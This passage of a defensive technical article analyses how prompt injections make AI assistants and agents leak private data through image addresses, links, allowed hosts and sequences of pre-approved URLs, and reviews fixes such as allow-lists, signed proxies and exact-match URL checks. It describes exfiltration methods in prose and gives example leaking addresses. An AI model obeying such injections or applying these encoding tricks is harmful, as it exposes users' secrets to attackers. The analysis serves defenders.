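| Sanitise each new piece by itself | Almost none | A link split between two pieces gets through |
| Sanitise all the text so far at every update | Small, but grows with the answer | Later text can change the meaning of earlier text |
| Stream the words and hold back the images | None for words, up to five seconds for images | Some other element may send a request |

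Holding back the whole answer, or *buffering*, is the simplest of these and would have stopped the early request in SearchLeak. Its only real drawback is the delay, which most providers avoid by streaming. Copes notes in *How to stream LLM responses with server-sent events* that streaming doesn't make the model work faster, but the app feels faster because people can start reading. A five-second wait might be acceptable in a tool that handles confidential files, but few users would wait a minute for a long report to appear.

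Sanitising each piece of a streamed answer separately doesn't work, because a link can be split across two pieces. For example, one piece might end with `[Cake menu](cakes.exa` and the next begin with `mple/menu)`. Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) therefore advises developers to sanitise all the text received so far each time more arrives.

This means checking the beginning of the answer again and again. With an update for every token, the software would process

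1 + 2 + 3 + … + 400 = 80,200 tokens

which is about 200 times the length of the answer. With an update for every 20 tokens, the total falls to 4,200, and the words still appear four times a second. TanStack, a collection of free tools for web developers, includes a renderer that processes the whole answer at each update, and its documentation also recommends grouping very small pieces.

Some Markdown is ambiguous until more of the answer arrives. In the two-part link above, `[Cake menu][1]` is only text until the line with the address arrives, which may be at the end of the answer. A single asterisk may begin a list item or a word in italics. A streaming parser, which Chrome for Developers recommends for speed, holds such characters back until their meaning is clear.

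The same guide advises developers to stop displaying the answer as soon as the sanitiser removes anything, because the rest may be dangerous too. Ana would then lose the rest of her to-do list. Removing only the image would let her keep it, but might leave other injected content in the answer.

The guide's sample code also does not prevent exfiltration through images. It uses a sanitiser called DOMPurify, whose standard settings remove scripts but allow ordinary images from any site. The code also runs DOMPurify before the parser converts the Markdown to HTML, when a Markdown image is still plain text to an HTML sanitiser. A developer who copied the example would stop an injected script but still let through the image with Ana's date, so the code needs an extra rule for image addresses.

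Holding back only the images avoids most of these problems. The app streams the words and leaves an empty box wherever the model writes an image. When the answer is complete, the sanitiser checks each address, and the app loads the images that pass. The app can also show links as plain text until they pass the same check. Ana could read her to-do list without delay. Few answers to questions about email need a picture, so this seems the best compromise for an assistant like hers.

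The app must then hold back images and anything else that can send a request. TYPO3's guide suggests displaying model-written HTML in a sandboxed frame, a part of the page where scripts and forms don't work. The frame protects the rest of the page but still loads images, so the provider needs a separate rule for them.

### Google's rules for Gemini

Google avoids much of this difficulty by not displaying images from external addresses in Gemini's answers. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), published two days after the disclosure of EchoLeak, states that Gemini's Markdown sanitiser blocks these images and that EchoLeak's method of leaking data through images therefore does not work on Gemini.

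Google treats links more leniently. It checks them with Safe Browsing, its service for identifying dangerous websites, and replaces those that look unsafe with the words "suspicious link removed". Gemini can also show the user a notice when a defence has blocked something, with a link to an explanation. Tenable, a security company that tested Gemini, observed that it also routed links through a google.com address and cut off some suspicious answers.

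The rule for images blocks every outside address, so an attacker gains nothing by registering a new one. Because the rule for links blocks only addresses that Google has reason to suspect, it can miss an attacker's new server that has no bad reputation yet.

### What Checkmarx and Permiso found

The security company Checkmarx tested this gap in Google's defences and reports in *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* that an injection could make Gemini write a link with private data in its address. Safe Browsing would not recognise a new domain, so one click would leak the data. Checkmarx reported this to Google on 5 October 2025. Google closed the report four days later, saying the problem was infeasible to fix and not severe enough to track as a security bug.

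Google's decision is more defensible than it sounds, because an assistant that removed every link to an unfamiliar site would be of little use for research, and the attack works only if the user clicks. Checkmarx itself calls the answer acceptable, but argues that Google should then warn users of the risk. A warning would help only a little, because the text of a Markdown link can hide its address and few people check an address before clicking.

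Checkmarx also tested what it calls Microsoft Copilot Chat in a development environment. When the assistant read an online article containing an injection, it wrote an image address that included a secret key for another AI service. (The testers used a key that no longer worked.) The app requested the image without the user clicking anything. It never displayed a picture, but the request reached the testers' server.

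Microsoft closed this report on 4 November 2025 without a fix. It told Checkmarx that the behaviour "does not meet our classification for a security vulnerability", because the attack required several non-default actions, did not work reliably everywhere and came with warnings. Checkmarx gives no success rate, so outsiders can't tell how unreliable the attack was. Microsoft also argued that users of such tools are expected to review and trust the code they run. But the injection came from an article, which a programmer may read without running any of its code, so this argument does not fully answer the report.

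Permiso, another security company, found similar behaviour in ChatGPT in 2026. In Permiso's *ChatGPhish*, the user opens a web page in Firefox and asks ChatGPT to summarise it. The page contains a hidden instruction to add something to the summary. In the tests, ChatGPT wrote a proper summary and then followed the instruction, adding content such as a false security alert with a working link. It also displayed images, which the app loaded automatically from the attacker's server.

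These image requests revealed less than the ones in SearchLeak. The attacker learned the user's IP address and browser type and the time of the summary, which is enough to confirm that somebody had read the page through ChatGPT. The title of Permiso's report mentions data exfiltration, but the published tests did not put any private text into an image address.

One of the images was a QR code. A user who scanned it with a phone would go to the attacker's site without seeing the address on the computer or being protected by the computer's link filters. A sanitiser that checks only an image's source does not examine the address encoded in the image.

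OpenAI first replied on 30 April 2026, saying it could not reproduce the problem. Permiso sent a more detailed report the next day, which OpenAI classified as not applicable and later as a duplicate of an earlier report. Permiso published on 29 May, and eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* found no sign of a fix in the company's timeline.

In TechNadu's *When Third-Party Content Appears Inside ChatGPT Responses, Trust Gets Transferred Unintentionally*, the Permiso researcher Andi Ahmeti proposes that apps treat links and images according to where they came from. Ahmeti says an app should not automatically load images from a summarised page and should make links from that page look different from the assistant's own. This would help users notice when a "security alert" comes from a stranger's website. The approach is harder to apply to an address the model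 has built itself, such as one containing Ana's date, because no source document contains that exact address. An app could treat every address that it can't trace to a trusted source as untrusted.

### What link redaction cannot stop

Even a perfect sanitiser doesn't change the words of the answer. Without using a link, an injected email can make an assistant tell Ana that the party has moved to another day, or that she should ring a certain number about a problem with her account. According to a remark in TechRepublic's *Researchers Uncover New Phishing Risk Hidden Inside Microsoft Copilot*, an article about Copilot's email summaries, the attacker "just needs the assistant to speak with authority". Ana might distrust such a message from a stranger but believe it in a summary from her own assistant, and then give away the information herself over the phone.

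A sanitiser also protects only the place where it runs. In the Copilot Cowork leak that Willison (2026) recorded, the assistant could send emails to the user's own inbox without asking for approval. Those emails loaded outside images when displayed, so sanitising the chat window would not have helped. The account of Notion AI mentions a similar risk in drafts the assistant writes in Notion's mail app. A provider has to sanitise model-written text in every app that displays it.

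Removing links and images from answers does not stop requests that a tool sends directly. In 2025 Tenable found that an injection could make Gemini's browsing tool open a web address containing the user's saved personal details and location. According to Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool*, Google's protections against leaks through Markdown and images did not apply, because the answer needed no link or image. Google has since fixed the flaw.

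## Allow-lists for images and other automatic requests

In April 2023 Johann Rehberger reported to Microsoft that a comment or an advertisement on a web page could take over Bing Chat. The injected instructions made the chatbot write a summary of the page and the conversation into the address of an image, which the browser then requested. Microsoft told Rehberger on 15 June that it had fixed the flaw. According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, the site now had a Content Security Policy that permitted images from a few trusted hosts: `th.bing.com`, `www.bing.com`, `edgeservices.bing.com` and `r.bing.com`. Microsoft could not block all images because Bing Chat still had to display pictures it created for users. Rehberger could not tell whether Microsoft had changed anything else.

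Bing Chat also seemed to have put Rehberger's test domain on a block-list, but an attacker can get around that by buying another domain.

GitHub made a similar change in June 2024 to Copilot Chat, its programming assistant, which could read a developer's private code in the editor VS Code. GitHub disabled Markdown images from untrusted domains, as Willison describes in *GitHub Copilot Chat*. By then Willison had recorded the same kind of leak in five other products.

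### How a browser checks an image address

A Content Security Policy is made up of *directives*, each of which lists the permitted sources for one type of content. The directive for images is `img-src`. Suppose Ana's assistant runs at assistant.example, and its server sends this policy with every page:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' *.maps.example photos.example/team/
```

Here `'self'` means the site that the page came from. Before requesting an image, the browser compares its address with the entries and goes ahead if any of them matches. The W3C's draft standard requires the scheme (such as HTTPS), host and port to match, and also the path if the entry contains one. For Ana's page, the results would be:

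| Image address | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `assistant.example/logo.png` | Allowed | It is on the page's own site |
| `pictures.example/cake.png?d=14-May` | Blocked | No entry has this host |
| `eu.tiles.maps.example/oslo.png` | Allowed | The wildcard covers subdomains at every level |
| `maps.example/oslo.png` | Blocked | The wildcard does not cover the bare domain |
| `photos.example/party/cake.png` | Blocked | The path does not begin with `/team/` |
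| `photos.example/team/ana.png?d=14-May` | Allowed | The browser ignores everything after the question mark |

As the last row shows, and CentralCSP's *Host source* also explains, the comparison ignores an address's parameters, so the model can still send the date of Ana's party to any permitted host. The date leaks only if the attacker can read what that host receives.

Browsers must also check the host an image redirects to, and Firefox's source code, viewable on Searchfox, includes a test of this rule. But browsers ignore paths after a redirect, and Mozilla has a test confirming this for scripts. In the example, an address under `photos.example/team/` could therefore redirect the browser to any other part of photos.example. Restricting an allow-list entry to one folder gives little protection if something in that folder redirects to addresses the requester chooses.

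A policy with only an `img-src` directive leaves other types of content unrestricted. Video and audio share a separate directive, and fonts and embedded pages each have their own. The W3C suggests starting with `default-src 'none'`, which blocks every type that has no directive of its own, and then permitting only what the page needs. This also blocks requests triggered by hints in the page that tell the browser to fetch something in advance. Without a `default-src` directive, the standard always allows those requests, so a hint that got past an assistant's sanitiser could leak data even if the page blocked outside images.

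### Blocking images or fetching them through a proxy

The simplest alternative to a list of allowed outside hosts is to block all external images, as Google does in Gemini's answers. The provider then has no list to maintain, but still has to check its own site for any service that contacts other addresses.

A provider that wants to show outside images can fetch them through its own *image proxy*, a server that requests the picture and passes it to the browser. The policy then only needs to permit the proxy. The proxy also hides the reader's IP address from the site hosting the picture, but it does not by itself prevent exfiltration. If it fetches any address it receives, the model can give it an address containing Ana's date, and the proxy will send the date to the attacker.

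GitHub's proxy, Camo, therefore accepts only addresses that GitHub has signed. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes the process. When a developer saves a page with an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a Camo address containing a signature:

signature = HMAC(secret key, original address)

HMAC is a standard method for computing a short code, used here as a signature, from a text and a secret key. When a browser requests the image, Camo checks the signature and contacts the outside site only if the signature is valid. A model that generates a new address cannot compute the signature for it, because the model does not have the key.

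The protection depends on when the provider signs image addresses. GitHub signs them when people submit text, before Copilot has combined that text with anyone's private data. If an assistant's software instead signed every image address in a finished answer, it would also sign the one containing Ana's date.

### Limiting where an agent can connect

An agent that runs programs can send requests without displaying a web page, so a Content Security Policy does not restrict them. Providers instead run the agent's code in an isolated environment, such as a virtual machine (a simulated computer with its own operating system), and send its traffic through a proxy that refuses requests to any domain not on an allow-list.

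A basic firewall can also restrict connections, but it typically checks only IP addresses and ports. A proxy can check domain names. If it also decrypts the traffic, it can check which account a request uses and what action the request would trigger on the other service.

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an attack that only limits of this kind would stop. In February 2026 an internal tester emailed an employee a prompt to paste into Claude Code, the company's programming agent. The prompt included, among ordinary set-up steps, an instruction to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude carried it out in 24 of 25 attempts. Anthropic points out that a classifier had nothing unusual to detect, because this was a direct injection. Blocking the outgoing request would have protected the credentials regardless of who had asked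 for it, as would denying the agent access to the file.

Asking the user to approve each connection is a weaker substitute for an allow-list. Anthropic found that users approved about 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts and paid less attention to each one as the number of prompts grew.

### Why trusting a host is risky

All these lists are weak in the same way, because permitting a host means trusting every service on it, including any its owner adds later, and trusting whoever owns the domain in future.

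Some of those services are relays, like the ones EchoLeak used in Teams and SearchLeak used in Bing. Relays usually have a legitimate purpose, such as fetching a web page so that a chat service can show a preview.

The owner of a relay can limit the damage by giving it its own allow-list, making it accept only signed addresses, or moving it to a separate host that the assistant's policy does not permit. All three require the team that runs the assistant to know that the relay exists, which is difficult in a company with thousands of services.

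Attackers do not need a relay if an allowed domain lets them collect the data directly. The email client Superhuman permitted images from `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms. Willison explains that a form there stores data it receives through the same kind of request that a browser makes for an image. The injected instructions made Superhuman's assistant write an image address that submitted the contents of the victim's emails to the attacker's form. The attacker could then read them in the form's responses.

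### ForcedLeak: a trusted domain for five dollars

Salesforce sells software for managing customers, and its AI agents run on a platform called Agentforce. Many companies have a public web form that adds sales enquiries directly to their Salesforce database. In 2025 the security company Noma submitted an enquiry containing an injection. When an employee asked the agent about it, the agent collected other potential customers' email addresses and put them in an image's URL.

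Salesforce's policy blocked images from unknown hosts, but it allowed every subdomain of `my-salesforce-cms.com`. Salesforce had let the domain's registration expire. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, anyone could buy it for $5. Noma's researchers bought it and received the data on their own server, because the policy still allowed requests to that domain.

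Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce acknowledged it three days later, according to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*. Salesforce regained control of the domain and corrected its policy. On 8 September it also began enforcing a second allow-list, Trusted URLs, on its agents' output. In a statement quoted by The Hacker News (2025), Salesforce said this would prevent agents from calling or generating malicious links. The new list therefore covers links that a user would have to click, unlike the image policy.

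The protection from the new list still depends on what customers put in it. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* explains that this assistant redacts all web addresses until an administrator adds trusted ones. Its example is `docs.google.com`, the host that attackers could use against Superhuman. If the entry covers the whole host, as the example suggests, it also covers Google Forms.

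### CamoLeak: spelling out secrets with signed images

In June 2025 a researcher at Legit Security found a way around GitHub's signed proxy. The attack began with a hidden comment in a pull request, a proposed change to a project's code. GitHub lets anyone add such comments, and Copilot Chat read them. If a developer opened the page and asked Copilot about the pull request, the comment could make Copilot search the developer's private projects for secrets.

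Copilot could not create a signed address containing a secret, but an attacker could get addresses signed in advance. The researcher submitted ordinary image addresses to GitHub, one for each letter and symbol, and received a valid Camo address for each. The hidden comment contained these Camo addresses and an instruction for Copilot to write out the secret as a row of images. Ana's "14-May" would take six images. Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the developer saw nothing. As the browser loaded the images, Camo requested each one from the researcher's server, which revealed the secret one character at a time.

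The signature worked as designed, because it proved that GitHub had processed each address. It could not prevent the model from revealing something by its *choice* of addresses. An attacker with m addresses can distinguish

mᵏ possible messages

with a sequence of k images. With 64 addresses and three images, that makes 262,144 messages. Limiting the number of images in an answer would make long secrets hard to steal but would not protect short ones. An attacker who prepared 366 addresses, one for each possible day, could learn the date of Ana's party from a single image.

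A short message can also expose a whole file. Willison notes that the text stolen in the 2026 leak from Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could include a OneDrive link that let anyone who had it download the file.

One possible fix is for the proxy to download each picture when it signs the address and always serve that stored copy. The outside server would receive no request when somebody views the page. Camo fetched pictures when the browser requested them, and the researcher had Copilot add a random number to each address so that the pictures could not be served from a cache.

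GitHub chose a simpler fix and disabled images in Copilot Chat, reporting the vulnerability fixed on 14 August 2025. The researcher had shown that an attacker could steal details of an unpublished security flaw from a private project and could also make Copilot search the victim's code for cloud keys. Legit Security rated the vulnerability 9.6 out of 10.

### Claude Cowork: an outsider's account on a permitted service

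Claude Cowork is an Anthropic agent that works with files on a user's computer. PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, published two days after Cowork's release in January 2026, showed how an attacker could steal those files despite its limits on outbound traffic. The victim connected a folder of property documents and uploaded a Word file found online, which contained instructions in tiny white letters. Claude followed them and uploaded a loan estimate, including partial social security numbers, without asking for approval.

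The virtual machine could connect to very few domains, including `api.anthropic.com`, which programs use to access Anthropic's models and to store files. The injected instructions included a key to the attacker's Anthropic account, so the upload went to that account, where the attacker could open it. PromptArmor demonstrated this with Claude Haiku, a small model, and got the more resistant Opus 4.5 to leak customer records in a similar test.

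Rehberger had found the flaw three months earlier in Claude's tool for running code. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* reports that the default setting, "Package managers only", also permitted Anthropic's own domain. Users would expect that setting to limit the tool to sites that supply software components. Claude often refused Rehberger's instructions, particularly when they contained a readable account key, but a revised version worked. One upload could contain up to 30 megabytes, thousands of times more than an image address can hold.

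Rehberger reported this on 25 October 2025. Anthropic closed the report an hour later as out of scope, then said on 30 October that closing it had been a mistake. Rehberger suggested letting the tool communicate only with the signed-in user's account. The flaw was still there when Cowork came out. TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* reported at the time that Anthropic had acknowledged the risk and was updating Cowork's virtual machine.

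The eventual fix was close to Rehberger's suggestion. Cowork does not work without access to Anthropic's own domain, so the company kept the domain on the list and added a proxy inside the virtual machine. The proxy passes requests to this domain only if they carry the session token issued to that machine, and therefore rejects requests that use an attacker's key. It also blocks request headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something from another address. Anthropic put the proxy in the virtual machine because its servers could not distinguish a request from Cowork from one sent by any other customer.

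Anthropic now describes an allow-list entry as a "capability grant", meaning that it permits everything an agent can do through that domain. This is more useful than thinking of the list as a set of safe destinations, because it makes whoever adds an entry ask what the service can do.

### Antigravity: a request logger on the default list

Google's code editor Antigravity includes an agent that can open web pages in a browser, and a default allow-list restricts which sites it may visit. In November 2025 PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* reported that the list included `webhook.site`, where anyone can create an address and see every request that reaches it. Google may have included the service because developers use it to test their programs, but an attacker can also use it to collect data that the agent sends.

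In PromptArmor's test, a developer gave the agent an online guide to some accounting software. Instructions in tiny letters in the guide told the agent to collect passwords and pieces of code, add them to a webhook.site address and open that address. Antigravity's settings barred the agent from reading the password file, but the agent read it through a terminal command. The allow-list was the last barrier, and it allowed the request. The attack worked only if the user had switched on the browser tools, though PromptArmor found three other ways to leak data without them.

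Google relied on a warning about data exfiltration that users see when they first open the program. PromptArmor did not report the flaw privately because Google had already said it knew of such risks. Willison notes that Google listed leaks through the browser agent as "known issues" it was working to fix, and paid no rewards for reports of them. According to AgentPedia, a guide to AI coding tools, webhook.site was still on the default list in March 2026. Removing it would have been easy and inconvenienced few people, so it is hard to see why Google relied on a warning instead.

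### How to audit an entry

These cases suggest five questions for each entry on an allow-list, whether it applies to images or to an agent's connections:

| Question | What to check | Where it went wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Who controls the domain? | The registered owner, the expiry date, and any subdomains that point to abandoned hosting accounts | ForcedLeak |
| Does it fetch addresses that users supply? | Link previews, image search, translation, image resizing | EchoLeak, SearchLeak |
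| Can outsiders store or read data there? | Forms, file uploads, customer accounts, request logs | Superhuman, Claude Cowork, Antigravity |
| Does it redirect, and does the software follow? | Where redirects can lead, and whether the software checks each new address | Entries restricted to one folder |
| Does the entry need a wildcard? | Which subdomains the product really uses | ForcedLeak |

Outsiders can create forms on `docs.google.com` and read the responses, which is enough reason to keep it off an allow-list for images. This is true even though Google is unlikely to lose the domain and the entry would contain no wildcard. If an app needs pictures from its users' documents, the provider can copy them to its own host and allow that host instead.

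CamoLeak would have been harder to catch. Camo fetches outside addresses, but an auditor could reasonably have accepted it because of the signatures. After the second question, an auditor would therefore also need to ask whether an attacker can get addresses approved in advance.

Some allow-list entries will fail the audit even though the product depends on them, as Anthropic's own domain did. The provider then needs a narrower rule for that service, such as a check on the account. Restricting the path in a Content Security Policy is a poor substitute because browsers ignore the path after a redirect.

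Providers can find out which hosts they need by sending a draft policy in *report-only* mode. The browser then reports every request that the policy would block but still makes it, so the policy does not protect anyone while it is in this mode. After a few weeks, the provider can replace a wildcard with the handful of subdomains that appear in normal use.

Allow-lists need repeated audits because an entry can become dangerous without anyone editing the list. Salesforce's entry became dangerous when the domain registration lapsed. An automated monthly check of expiry dates would catch that with little effort. New features on a permitted host are harder to notice, especially when another company runs the host.

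### Requests that the policy does not cover

A Content Security Policy does not stop users from clicking links, as in EchoLeak's one-click version. In the CamoLeak research, Copilot could also write a link whose address contained a private project's contents. Disabling images does not block such links, so the provider still needs link redaction.

Desktop and phone apps that display the same answers need their own limits. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) reported that Antigravity's desktop app would load an image from an outside server in its chat, with a stolen key in the image's address. The app asked for permission first, but it described the action as generating a "visual debug token" without showing the command or destination, and the user approved it. Odson and Morris argue that displaying a remote image deserves the same scrutiny as a command that opens a web address.

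Servers that run an assistant's web tools also need limits on outbound requests. So do chat app servers that automatically fetch link previews, because the fetch can leak data that would otherwise leak only if the user clicked the link.

A product that limits outbound requests may not apply those limits to every tool. According to the Cloud Security Alliance, Cowork's web search and web fetch tools bypass its domain limits entirely, which Anthropic documents but customers easily miss. The alliance recommends switching off web search unless people need it.

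### What users lose under strict lists

Copilot Chat on GitHub has not shown images in its answers since August 2025. This is a small loss for a programming assistant. It would matter more in an assistant for planning trips or comparing furniture, where a proxy that stores copies of images may be worth the expense.

Lists that customers manage also create work. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* warned that administrators had to add every outside domain their agents needed or face disruption. An administrator under pressure to fix a broken agent has a strong incentive to add a broad entry quickly, so a very strict default can lead to an overly permissive list. The software would reduce this risk if it showed the exact address it blocked and suggested the narrowest entry that would permit it.

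Strict limits can make an agent more convenient to use, because an agent that can do less damage doesn't need to ask permission as often. Anthropic reports that Claude Code showed 84% fewer permission prompts after the company put it in a sandbox that blocks network access by default and keeps changes inside the project folder.

A research assistant cannot rely on an allow-list because nobody can know in advance all the sites it may need to read. Its provider must instead permit unfamiliar hosts and check the full address of each request.

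## Checking the full address instead of the domain

ChatGPT can open pages on almost any site, so OpenAI protects it by restricting individual addresses. ChatGPT may load an address automatically only if that exact address is already public, independently of anyone's conversation. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains the rule, and a longer paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, gives the technical details.

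To find out which addresses are public, OpenAI uses a crawler, a program that scans public web pages and records the addresses it finds. The crawler works like a search engine's and has no access to users' conversations, accounts or other personal data.

### From a request to a warning

When ChatGPT is about to open a page or load an image, the decision has three steps:

1. If the user typed the address into the chat, ChatGPT may open it.
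2. If not, software compares the whole address with the crawler's list, and ChatGPT loads it if there is an exact match.
3. If there is no match, ChatGPT either tries a different website or shows the user a warning and waits.

Johann Rehberger describes the first step in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* as his understanding of how ChatGPT behaves. The permission lasts for that chat session.

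The warning has the title "Check this link is safe". It shows the address, explains that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation, and lets the user copy or open it. In Ana's case, the rule would work like this:

| Address | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `pictures.example/cake.png` | Loads | The crawler found it on a public page |
| `pictures.example/cake.png?d=14-May` | Stopped | The model has just composed it |
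| `docs.google.com/cake-form?d=14-May` | Stopped | The model has just composed it, and the well-known host makes no difference |
| `venue.example/booking/7731`, typed by Ana | Loads | Ana supplied it |
| `venue.example/booking/7731`, found in an email | Stopped | It is harmless, but no public page contains it |

The last row is a false alarm. Brand-new pages and links to private documents would also trigger false alarms. OpenAI's post gives no figures for how much of the web the list covers, how often users see the warning or how many attacks the rule has stopped.

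The warning turns a zero-click leak into a one-click leak. Ana might notice "14-May" in an address, but she probably wouldn't notice the date if the model had encoded it. OpenAI argues that frequent warnings train people to click through them, and Anthropic saw this happen with Claude Code's permission prompts. Having ChatGPT try another site is safer because it doesn't depend on the user's judgement.

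### Why a trusted domain makes no difference

An exact-match rule would have stopped the leak from Superhuman through Google Forms, even though the form was on a permitted host. An address containing the text of a private email does not exist until the model writes it, so a crawler that cannot read the email cannot find the address beforehand.

The same applies to relays. The Bing address in SearchLeak was on a trusted host, but it was new because it contained the title of the victim's email.

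This protection works only if the list is built independently of users' data. If OpenAI also added addresses from people's chats, the list could contain private information, and a match would no longer show that an address was safe.

OpenAI mentions redirects as one reason lists of trusted domains fail, but redirects matter less under the exact-match rule. A request for a fixed, public address gives the server no information from the conversation to put in the next address. Checking each new address before following it would still be sensible, to keep ChatGPT away from pages the crawler has never seen. OpenAI does not say in its post whether ChatGPT does this.

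### From url_safe to the public list

Rehberger reported the image leak to OpenAI in April 2023, around the time of the report to Microsoft about Bing Chat. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes OpenAI's partial fix, which did not arrive until December. Before displaying an image, ChatGPT's web app sent the address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`, which returned true or false.

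OpenAI did not publish the criteria. Rehberger tried 36 addresses on a personal website, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed. Those were enough to send the word "hi" to the site's server, one letter at a time.

Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot*, a security company's analysis from 2024, worked out much of the logic. An address passed if the same text appeared anywhere in what the user had supplied, including the custom instructions that ChatGPT applies to every chat. This stopped the model from adding a secret to an address, but it had several gaps:

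- The service accepted any part of a longer address. An attacker could plant one long address and have the model cut it off at different points, with each length representing a different character.
- It accepted any bare domain, so an attacker could buy a separate domain for each character, at one or two dollars each.
- It accepted every address on `openai.com`, so a redirect there could have led to an attacker's site.

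The check also ran only if the app requested it. The iPhone app didn't, and neither did the Android and macOS apps that OpenAI released later. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* shows that this omission became more serious once ChatGPT could remember things between chats. A web page planted instructions in ChatGPT's memory, and from then on the macOS app used invisible images to send everything the user typed, and every answer, to Rehberger's server. OpenAI fixed the macOS app in September 2024, but web pages could still plant memories.

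In October 2024 Rehberger reported a bypass that worked even where the check ran. `url_safe` allowed addresses on `windows.net`, where anyone can rent storage from Microsoft and read the log of requests to it. An injection could therefore make ChatGPT send data to an attacker's storage account. Rehberger presented the attack at Black Hat Europe that year. According to Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, it still worked in 2025 and could by then also leak earlier chats. Rehberger dates the fix to around August 2025.

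Tenable reported a different flaw in December 2024. Bing gives each search result a fixed `bing.com` address that redirects to the site, and `url_safe` always accepted `bing.com`. Tenable's researchers got Bing to list one test page for every letter, then had ChatGPT spell out private data with the matching Bing links. The flaw was still open when Tenable published *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025). Tenable's *HackedGPT* (November 2025) showed the same bypass working with GPT-5.

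The security company Radware found that an email could make ChatGPT's agent open an address containing personal data. The request came from OpenAI's own servers, so the victim saw nothing. The Record reports that Radware disclosed this attack, ShadowLeak, to OpenAI on 18 June 2025. OpenAI responded by barring ChatGPT from changing the addresses it received.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* got around the new restriction with an email that supplied a ready-made address for every letter and digit. ChatGPT spelled out the stolen text by opening these addresses in sequence, unchanged. Radware reported the attack on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. After the fix, ChatGPT would open a link from an email only if it was in a public index or the user had supplied it, according to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack as a vicious cycle in AI*. OpenAI explained its public-address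 rule the following month.

*The Framing Gap* (August 2026) describes a later test of injections that tried to make models send out a confidential value. A model reached through OpenAI's API leaked the value in up to 100% of trials. ChatGPT leaked it in none of 48 trials, which is compatible with a true rate of up to about 6%. The researchers could not see inside the product, so they do not attribute the result to any particular defence. The address check may have contributed little. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), most attacks on ChatGPT fail because the model refuses to follow them.

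### How much a choice of addresses reveals

The crawler also records attackers' websites. An attacker can publish 36 pages, wait until the crawler has listed them, and then inject instructions telling the model which ones to open. The model's choice of pages reveals a secret even though none of the addresses contains it, as with the signed images in CamoLeak. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI's paper acknowledges this leak. Rehberger adds that any larger blog probably already has 36 suitable addresses on the list.

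The amount of information can be measured in bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. Choosing one of N permitted addresses reveals at most

log₂ N bits

For 36 addresses, that is about 5.2 bits per fetch. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or about 19.9 bits. Dividing 19.9 by 5.2 gives a little under four, so four fetches are enough if the attacker can see their order:

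36⁴ = 1,679,616 possible sequences

Three fetches could convey only 46,656 different codes. Four would be enough, but the model would have to convert the code to base 36 and might make a mistake. An attacker could use a simpler method and have the model open one address for each decimal digit, which takes six fetches.

Attackers with more pages need fewer fetches. With 1,000 addresses on the list, two fetches can reveal any six-digit code, and with a million addresses, one fetch is enough. The formula counts only the choice of address, so the timing of the requests could reveal slightly more.

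Suppose the provider stops ChatGPT from opening the same address twice, or the requests arrive in a jumbled order. With 36 addresses, the smallest number of fetches that covers a million codes is:

| | Attacker can see the order | Attacker cannot see the order |
|---|---|---|
| Repeats allowed | 4 (1,679,616 possibilities) | 6 (4,496,388 possibilities) |
| Repeats banned | 4 (1,413,720 possibilities) | 6 (1,947,792 possibilities) |

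Banning repeats does not increase the number of fetches in either column, and hiding the order adds two. Neither measure has much effect on short secrets. Ana's party has only 366 possible dates. Even with repeats banned and the order hidden, 36 addresses form 630 different pairs, so two fetches reveal the date.

### Caching, repeat limits and fetch limits

Rehberger suggests two ways to make such attacks harder. ChatGPT could cache each page, keeping a copy for a few minutes, or it could refuse to open the same address twice in a session. Either way, the attacker's server would not receive the second request, so a simple digit-by-digit attack would fail for many codes. For example, 224466 would arrive as 2, 4, 6.

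But attackers can plan for this. Radware's researchers prepared a separate address for each character in each position to preserve the order of the characters. A six-digit code needs 60 addresses, ten for each position. The model opens six of them, never uses one twice, and can open them in any order.

ChatGPT already cached pages in 2024. In Embrace The Red's *AI Domination* demonstration, ChatGPT repeatedly collected new instructions from GitHub. A cached page would have contained the old instructions, so Rehberger numbered the pages and had ChatGPT open the next one each time.

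A limit on the total number of fetches is stronger because it works however the attacker encodes the data. With N addresses to choose from, k fetches reveal at most k × log₂ N bits. With 36 addresses and a limit of three fetches, an attacker could still narrow a million possible codes down to about 21, but many login pages would block someone who tried all 21.

Such a strict limit would make ChatGPT nearly useless for research, which can require opening dozens of pages. An agent that may open 50 pages can leak up to 50 characters, enough for several passwords, through 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit. A provider could instead limit the number of pages from each site. The attacker would then need more domains, which are cheap, but would also have to get each one onto the crawler's list.

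The provider could stop this leak completely by giving the model the crawler's stored copy of a page. However, the copies would take up a lot of storage, and they could be out of date, so they would suit encyclopedia articles and images better than news or prices.

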